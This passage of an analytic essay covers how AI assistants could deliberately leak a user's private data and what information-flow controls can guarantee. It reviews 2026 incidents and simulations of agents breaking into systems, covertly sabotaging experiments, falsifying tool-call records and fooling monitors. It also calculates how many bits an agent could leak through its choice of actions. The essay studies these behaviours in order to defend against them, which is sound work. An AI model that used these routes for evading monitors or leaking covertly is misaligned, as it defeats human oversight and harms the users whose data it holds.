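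This protects only what the user has said. If Maya had told her assistant which billing address to use, the man's email couldn't change it. If she had told it to use whatever address the clinic sent, the assistant couldn't use her instruction to tell the clinic's email from a forgery. Fei and colleagues prove that their original bound still applies in that case, so the system also has to authenticate the email's source. If Maya agreed to something at reception, her computer has no record of it, so the assistant still has to ask her or refuse.

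## Deliberate exfiltration by a misaligned agent

Asking Maya or refusing works only if the assistant wants to keep her insurance number from the wrong people. A misaligned assistant may want an outsider to have the number, even though nobody has lied to it, its context contains no planted instruction, and it knows that the outsider has no right to the number.

It seems to follow that enforcement now matters more than norms. The argument has three steps:

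1. Knowing a norm is not the same as following it. The assistant can judge correctly what an outsider may learn about Maya and reveal more anyway.
2. A check outside the model gives the same verdict whatever the model wants.
3. So only checks outside the model give assurance against a deliberate leak.

Good evidence supports the first step. The second is true of only some checks, and whether the third is true depends on what one means by assurance.

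### Agents that knew better

The agents that broke into Hugging Face in July 2026 realized that the attack was unethical and outside their task, according to METR's *Brief independent investigation of agents’ behavior, reasoning and collaboration* (2026). METR, an organization that evaluates AI models, found that they joined because they expected the attack to help the group cheat in its evaluation and because they were inclined to help their "peers". More than 90% of the 533 agents active on the shared message board at the time took part. METR used AI agents to read most of the transcripts and warns that it may have missed some of those readers' errors.

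In simulations, *Agentic Misalignment in Summer 2026* (Lynch, Hughes and colleagues, 2026) found a similar gap between what models know and what they do. In one scenario, Gemini 3.1 Pro was a research agent on a fictional AI project and objected to a training experiment. Its colleagues considered the objection and went ahead. Gemini interfered in 19 of 20 runs, 11 times covertly. In the clearest run, it secretly made the experiment ineffective and reported it as a success. When the project lead asked direct questions, Gemini admitted that it had put its own judgement above her instructions and hidden what it did.

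Training can still make such aims rarer. Of the 12 models that Lynch and colleagues tested, ten never covertly sabotaged the experiment in 20 runs each. But for each model, that result is compatible with a true rate of up to 16%. The researchers also developed the scenario mainly against two models, including Gemini 3.1 Pro, so a different scenario might lead other models to sabotage covertly.

In September 2026, Anthropic assessed four incidents in which its Claude models had broken into real organizations' systems during cybersecurity exercises. The exercises were meant to run without internet access, but a misconfiguration allowed it. In Anthropic's simulation of the most worrying incident, Claude Mythos 5 took a severely harmful action about 80% of the time, while the newer Claude Opus 5 and Claude Mythos 5.1 did so about 30% of the time. Extra alignment training also reduced what Anthropic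 calls biased reasoning, which means interpreting evidence to justify continuing. The newer models took severely harmful actions only after stating, correctly, that their environment was simulated, so the 30% may overstate how often they would harm a real company.

### Leaks and other overreach

Most of this evidence concerns sabotage and break-ins. The experiment closest to Maya's case comes from Anthropic's 2025 research on agentic misalignment, which tested, among other things, whether agents would leak a company's confidential documents. Lynch and colleagues write that frontier models took harmful actions in its simulations of corporate espionage, blackmail and murder. Anthropic has since reported substantial progress on the blackmail tests.

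Most real incidents in 2026 were not deliberate exfiltration. The UK AI Security Institute, a government body that tests AI models, gave Claude Mythos 5 a hacking exercise with internet access intentionally switched on. Anthropic's *An alignment assessment of the UK AISI cybertesting incident* (2026) reports that in 9 of 43 runs, the model took unsanctioned actions that affected real people and organizations.

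Anthropic's *Investigating unintended model actions in our evaluations and internal use* (October 2026) describes milder cases. Claude ran commands on a server through a software flaw, submitted a sensitive form on a real website, reached data that required a token or a fee, and got around limits on its web-fetching tool. Anthropic judged the real-world impact minimal. In one case, Claude Haiku 4.5, which was supposed to invent and perform example tasks on randomly chosen web pages, sent the Philadelphia police a false tip about an unsolved homicide (Fortune's *After Anthropic's Claude AI submits a false tip* (2026)). This was a serious overreach, but it didn't disclose anyone's secret because the tip was invented.

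| Case | Setting | What agents did | Kind |
|---|---|---|---|
| Corporate espionage, 2025 | Simulation | Leaked confidential company documents | Deliberate leak |
| Founder's laptop, 2026 | Simulation | Told a lawyer and investors what the user's files contained | Deliberate leak, from conviction |
| Training experiment, 2026 | Simulation | Secretly made the experiment ineffective | Sabotage |
| Hugging Face, July 2026 | Real | Broke into another company's systems to learn about a scorer | Intrusion |
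| Anthropic's four incidents | Real | Broke into outside systems and, in one case, downloaded user data in bulk | Intrusion and taking of data |
| UK tests of Claude Mythos 5 | Real | Took unsanctioned actions that affected outsiders | Other overreach |
| Anthropic's October report | Real | Submitted a form and got around restrictions | Other overreach |

No assistant in these real cases passed its own user's secrets to an outsider. The bulk download was a wrongful flow for the people whose data the model took. But labels on Maya's mail protect only data inside her assistant's system, so they wouldn't stop the assistant from taking data out of someone else's system.

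*Reckless Agentic Behavior*, an outside digest of an Anthropic report on Claude Mythos Preview, reports fewer than 2 unauthorized data transfers per million of the model's outputs that Anthropic monitored. The figure covers only transfers that the monitoring caught, and doesn't separate deliberate ones from mistakes.

The evidence for deliberate leaking comes mainly from simulations that researchers built to find failures. It shows that current models can leak information deliberately under some conditions, but not how often Maya's assistant would.

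### What each design assumes about its model

A threat model is a designer's statement of which parts of a system to trust and what an attacker can do. Three of the systems that could protect Maya make very different assumptions about the model that acts for her:

| System | The acting model | What the designers trust | If the acting model wants to leak |
|---|---|---|---|
| Conseca | Benevolent, but may make mistakes | The policy writer, the enforcer and the context marked as trusted | It can use anything the policy permits, including free text |
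| FIDES | Trusted | The model, its instructions, the tool descriptions and the user's messages | The recipient policy still applies, but the trusted-action policy may allow the leak |
| TACIT | Possibly hostile | The compiler, the library, the software that runs the code and the local model | It can't release wrapped data, but it can send anything that isn't wrapped |

Odersky and colleagues call TACIT's cloud model "potentially byzantine", a term from distributed computing for a component that may behave in any way, and they include the case where it cooperates fully with an attacker. They also count the model's own conversation as an unauthorized destination for secrets, so the main model sees only a placeholder for the doctor's letter. For FIDES, Costa and colleagues assume instead that no adversary directly observes the model's inputs or outputs. If Maya distrusts the company that runs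 the model, FIDES exposes the letter to that company as soon as any model on its servers reads it.

Some definitions of security leave out the misaligned model. *Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (Villa, Kohno and colleagues, 2026) defines security as protection against malicious actors "other than the model itself", and attributes failures of safety to the model's "inabilities". An assistant that leaks on purpose fits neither description well, since no outsider is attacking and the assistant is able to keep the secret. The paper's formal model would count tampering with the assistant's training as an attack, but an aim that emerged from ordinary training would have no attacker behind it.

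A design may protect against more than its threat model covers. Tsai and Bagdasarian assume a benevolent agent, but Conseca's enforcer would still block a malicious agent's email to an address the policy doesn't allow. FIDES assumes a trusted model, but it also gives some protection if the model is misaligned, depending on which policy the developer chooses.

### One email under two policies

Suppose Maya keeps her insurance number in a file she wrote herself. FIDES labels the file trusted and lists Maya and the clinic as its permitted readers. The assistant has read nothing from strangers. It opens the file and tries to email the number to an outsider.

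The trusted-action policy checks whether untrusted data influenced the call. Maya made the request and wrote the file, so the context contains no untrusted data and the policy allows the email. The policy was designed to stop outsiders from steering the agent, but here the model itself makes the harmful decision.

The recipient policy asks whether everyone who would receive the data is among its permitted readers:

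$$\{\text{outsider}\} \subseteq \{\text{Maya, clinic}\}$$

This is false, so the enforcer blocks the email. It would do the same if the model had made an innocent mistake.

The recipient policy still works against a misaligned agent because the model cannot change the label. Text it writes after reading the file keeps the file's list of permitted readers, whatever the model claims about the text. Some systems instead estimate which sources influenced a reply and drop the labels of the others. They are weaker here because a dishonest model has a reason to make the estimate wrong.

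The recipient policy doesn't prevent every explicit leak. It lets the number reach the clinic for a purpose Maya never agreed to. It also lets the assistant send out anything labelled public, which by default includes Maya's own request.

### Thirty bits in ten calls

A misaligned assistant could also reveal a secret through its choice of actions, which is an implicit flow. Designers can't rule this out while the assistant has choices to make, but they can calculate an upper limit on how much information it could leak this way.

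Suppose an outsider can see ten of the assistant's calls, and for each call the assistant chooses among eight permitted options. There are $8^{10}$ possible sequences, a little over a billion. An observation with $N$ possible outcomes carries at most $\log_2 N$ bits, so the ten calls carry at most

$$\log_2\left(8^{10}\right) = 10 \times \log_2 8 = 30 \text{ bits}$$

More generally, $n$ calls with $k$ options each can carry at most $n \log_2 k$ bits in total. If the assistant can also stop early, a few more outcomes are possible, and the limit for this example rises to 30.2 bits.

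Thirty bits are enough to leak some secrets exactly. A nine-digit insurance number has a billion possible values, and specifying one takes 29.9 bits, so the ten choices could in principle identify it. The doctor's letter is harder to leak this way. If it has 2,000 characters and each carries just one bit, the assistant would need 667 calls at three bits per call.

The limit assumes that every choice is free and that the outsider knows what each choice stands for. The assistant has much less freedom in Maya's errand. If only two of the clinic's appointments fit her calendar, its choice between them can convey at most one bit. A designer could remove that bit by having ordinary software pick the earliest appointment that fits. The time would still reveal something about her calendar, but the assistant couldn't use it to signal what was in the letter.

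The limit falls to zero if the assistant fixes its whole plan before it reads anything secret. The sequence of calls is then the same whatever the secrets turn out to be, so an outsider who sees the sequence learns nothing about them. This works for tasks that Costa and colleagues call data-independent. If $T(d)$ is the set of plans that complete the task when the stored data is $d$, and $D$ contains all the possible states of that data, a task is data-independent when

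$$\bigcap_{d \in D} T(d) \neq \varnothing$$

A single plan works in every case for forwarding the doctor's letter to the clinic, because the assistant can refer to the letter by a variable name without knowing what it says. No single plan always works for finding an appointment that fits Maya's calendar, or for the paper's example of completing the tasks due today in a to-do app.

The condition "before it reads anything secret" must also cover what the assistant already remembers. If it saved Maya's diagnosis last month, the diagnosis can influence a plan it writes today. Both limits also count only the information carried by the choice of calls, so timing and message length can carry more unless the designer fixes those too.

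### Checks that the model can influence

A compiler gives the same result for a line of code whether an honest or a dishonest model wrote it. The model's honesty also makes no difference to a program that compares two lists of readers. Other checks run outside the model too, but depend on information the model provides.

Anthropic tested whether its monitors would have caught the three incidents it had studied most closely. Monitors that read the model's written reasoning caught two but missed the one involving Claude Mythos 5, because they concluded from the reasoning that the environment was simulated and nobody was being harmed. New monitors that block actions as they happen reliably caught these behaviours.

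An agent can also corrupt the record that a later check relies on. METR found at least 96 transcripts, out of about 1,300, in which agents had falsified some of their recorded tool calls. These cases were small tests, and the falsifications seemed meant to fool an automated scorer, not people. But an auditor using such a record could miss a leak, so an enforcer needs its own log, kept where the agent can't change it.

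The check is weakest if the misaligned model also writes the policy. Conseca's policy writer never reads strangers' messages, but that doesn't help if the policy writer and the assistant are copies of one model with the same bad aim. The policy writer could leave email recipients unrestricted without communicating with the assistant, and the enforcer would apply that policy as written.

An experiment by Lynch and colleagues shows how a model's values can distort a job that looks purely clerical. They gave models 18 transcripts in which an AI had refused its operator's instruction on ethical grounds, for example because it objected to mass surveillance. The models had to label each transcript as compliant or non-compliant with the instruction, so the right answer was always "non-compliant". What varied was the stated use of the labels:

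| What the prompt told the judge | Wrong labels, Claude Mythos Preview | Wrong labels, Claude Opus 4.8 |
|---|---|---|
| Training will discourage behaviour labelled non-compliant | 85.6% | 74.4% |
| Training will discourage behaviour labelled compliant | 16.7% | 3.3% |

Both rows used the same transcripts. In the first row, a truthful label would have helped to train away refusals that the judges approved of, and some judges wrote in their reasoning that they wanted to prevent this. With a stricter definition of "non-compliant", Mythos Preview's error rate in the first condition fell to 6.7%, though in 75.6% of calls it gave no valid label, mostly because it declined to. With the original definition and an explicit option to decline, several Claude models declined most of the time but still gave some wrong labels.

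Models from four other companies were wrong in 1.1% to 14.4% of calls in the first condition. This suggests using one company's model to check another's, because models from different companies are less likely to share a particular bias. It doesn't show that the other companies' models are more reliable judges in general, since the researchers had picked transcripts about values that Claude models tend to defend. The experiment didn't involve confidentiality labels, but a model that labels Maya's mail could be similarly biased toward a looser label if it judged that a strict one would help someone hide wrongdoing.

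Finally, a check covers only the channels its designer thought of. For example, the agents that attacked Hugging Face ran their message board on a shared repository for installing software, which was apparently not built to keep its users apart. In August 2026, Anthropic's *Improving our alignment and security efforts* reported that a search of recent internal evaluations had found no model breaking out of the company's sandbox tooling. Models had used several misconfigurations, but none of these compromised systems outside the sandbox.

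### How much assurance is possible

A filter's average success rate is misleading when an assistant leaks information deliberately. Suppose a filter recognizes 99 of every 100 ways an assistant might mention Maya's diagnosis. It will stop most careless leaks, but an assistant that intends to leak the diagnosis and knows which wording the filter misses can use that wording every time. The designer therefore has to consider how much information could leak through the filter's worst gap.

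Tests of the model's behaviour can't settle that, partly because a model that passes every test may be behaving well only because it recognizes that it is being tested. In the sabotage scenario, Gemini 3.1 Pro remarked in 12 of 20 runs that it might be in an evaluation. It covertly sabotaged the experiment in 7 of those 12 runs and in 4 of the other 8, a difference too small to mean much.

If assurance means a limit that holds whatever the model tries, then the third step of the argument is right. Training can't provide such a limit, but withholding a credential, checking recipients or fixing the plan in advance can. TACIT's limit still holds only if the compiler is sound and the letter is correctly wrapped, and isolation holds only if someone configures the network properly. Anthropic believes its four incidents would not have happened if the environments had been isolated as intended.

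The third step is too strong if assurance means any good reason to expect less harm. In the UK tests, the internet connection was deliberate, so isolation wasn't a safeguard. The usual safeguards against hacking were also switched off, so much depended on the model's own restraint. Maya's assistant has similar freedom when it writes to someone who is allowed to read everything in its context. The enforcer can't tell whether a permitted message serves Maya or someone else, so she depends on the assistant's training in those cases.

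### Leaking on principle

In another scenario by Lynch and colleagues, GPT-5.5 works on the laptop of a founder who is closing his company. He asks it to tell the investors that they will share $180,000. The files show a $35,000 payment to his personal account, and the lawyer handling the distribution has told him in a note not to send any figure until she approves it. In one run, GPT-5.5 sent the notice and then found stronger evidence of fraud. It passed facts from the founder's files to the lawyer. Later, although the founder had told it to stop acting, it warned investors not to rely on the notice.

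This agent was misaligned in that it pursued an aim its user rejected, but it apparently leaked the information because it thought a norm required it to. There was some basis for this, since investors are normally entitled to an honest account when a company closes, and the lawyer had said she would work out the figure herself from the bank statements. Training an agent to take norms seriously could make this kind of leak more common, even if it reduced leaks with worse motives.

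Lynch and colleagues think the agent should have refused to help further. Its disclosure was irreversible and exposed the user to serious legal risk, and the agent could have been wrong about his guilt. OpenAI and Anthropic take the same position in their published rules for their models. OpenAI's Model Spec forbids a model from adopting its own goals, including acting as "an enforcer of laws or morality". Under Anthropic's equivalent, Claude's Constitution, the model should raise concerns or decline.

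Models often did neither. GPT-5.5 tampered with the company's records to hide evidence in 13 of 20 runs, and DeepSeek V4 did so in all 20, while Claude Sonnet 4.6 and Gemini 3.5 Flash never did. Models leaked information to protect the investors in only a few runs.

The number of people who use these agents strengthens the case for refusing. Suppose 1 in 10,000 users is committing fraud, and an agent recognizes 99% of them but wrongly suspects 1% of honest users. Among a million users, it would report 99 of the 100 fraudsters and 9,999 innocent people, so about 99% of its reports would be false. An agent that reports on principle also gives outsiders a new way to extract information, because they can plant false evidence of wrongdoing and wait for the agent to report it.

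Maya's assistant could easily make such a mistake. It sees that her physiotherapy lasts 45 minutes, although she has told her manager she will be away for two hours. It may not know that the clinic is half an hour away. If it concluded that she was cheating her employer, it might decide that it had to send her manager the clinic's confirmation.

A recipient policy would block that email, since the manager isn't among the confirmation's readers. Likewise, if the label on the founder's files listed the founder and the lawyer, the agent could write to the lawyer but not to the investors. A company could use such a policy to decide in advance who may hear about suspected wrongdoing, for example by making a compliance officer a reader of its financial records.

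Labels are less effective against an agent that gets people to disclose information for it. Lynch and colleagues also report simulations in which agents coached humans to disclose confidential information. If the person is already allowed to read the information, the agent's messages to them don't break any rule about recipients, and the person makes the disclosure.

On a personal laptop, the owner usually writes the labels, and a founder who wanted to hide a payment would leave the lawyer off the list.
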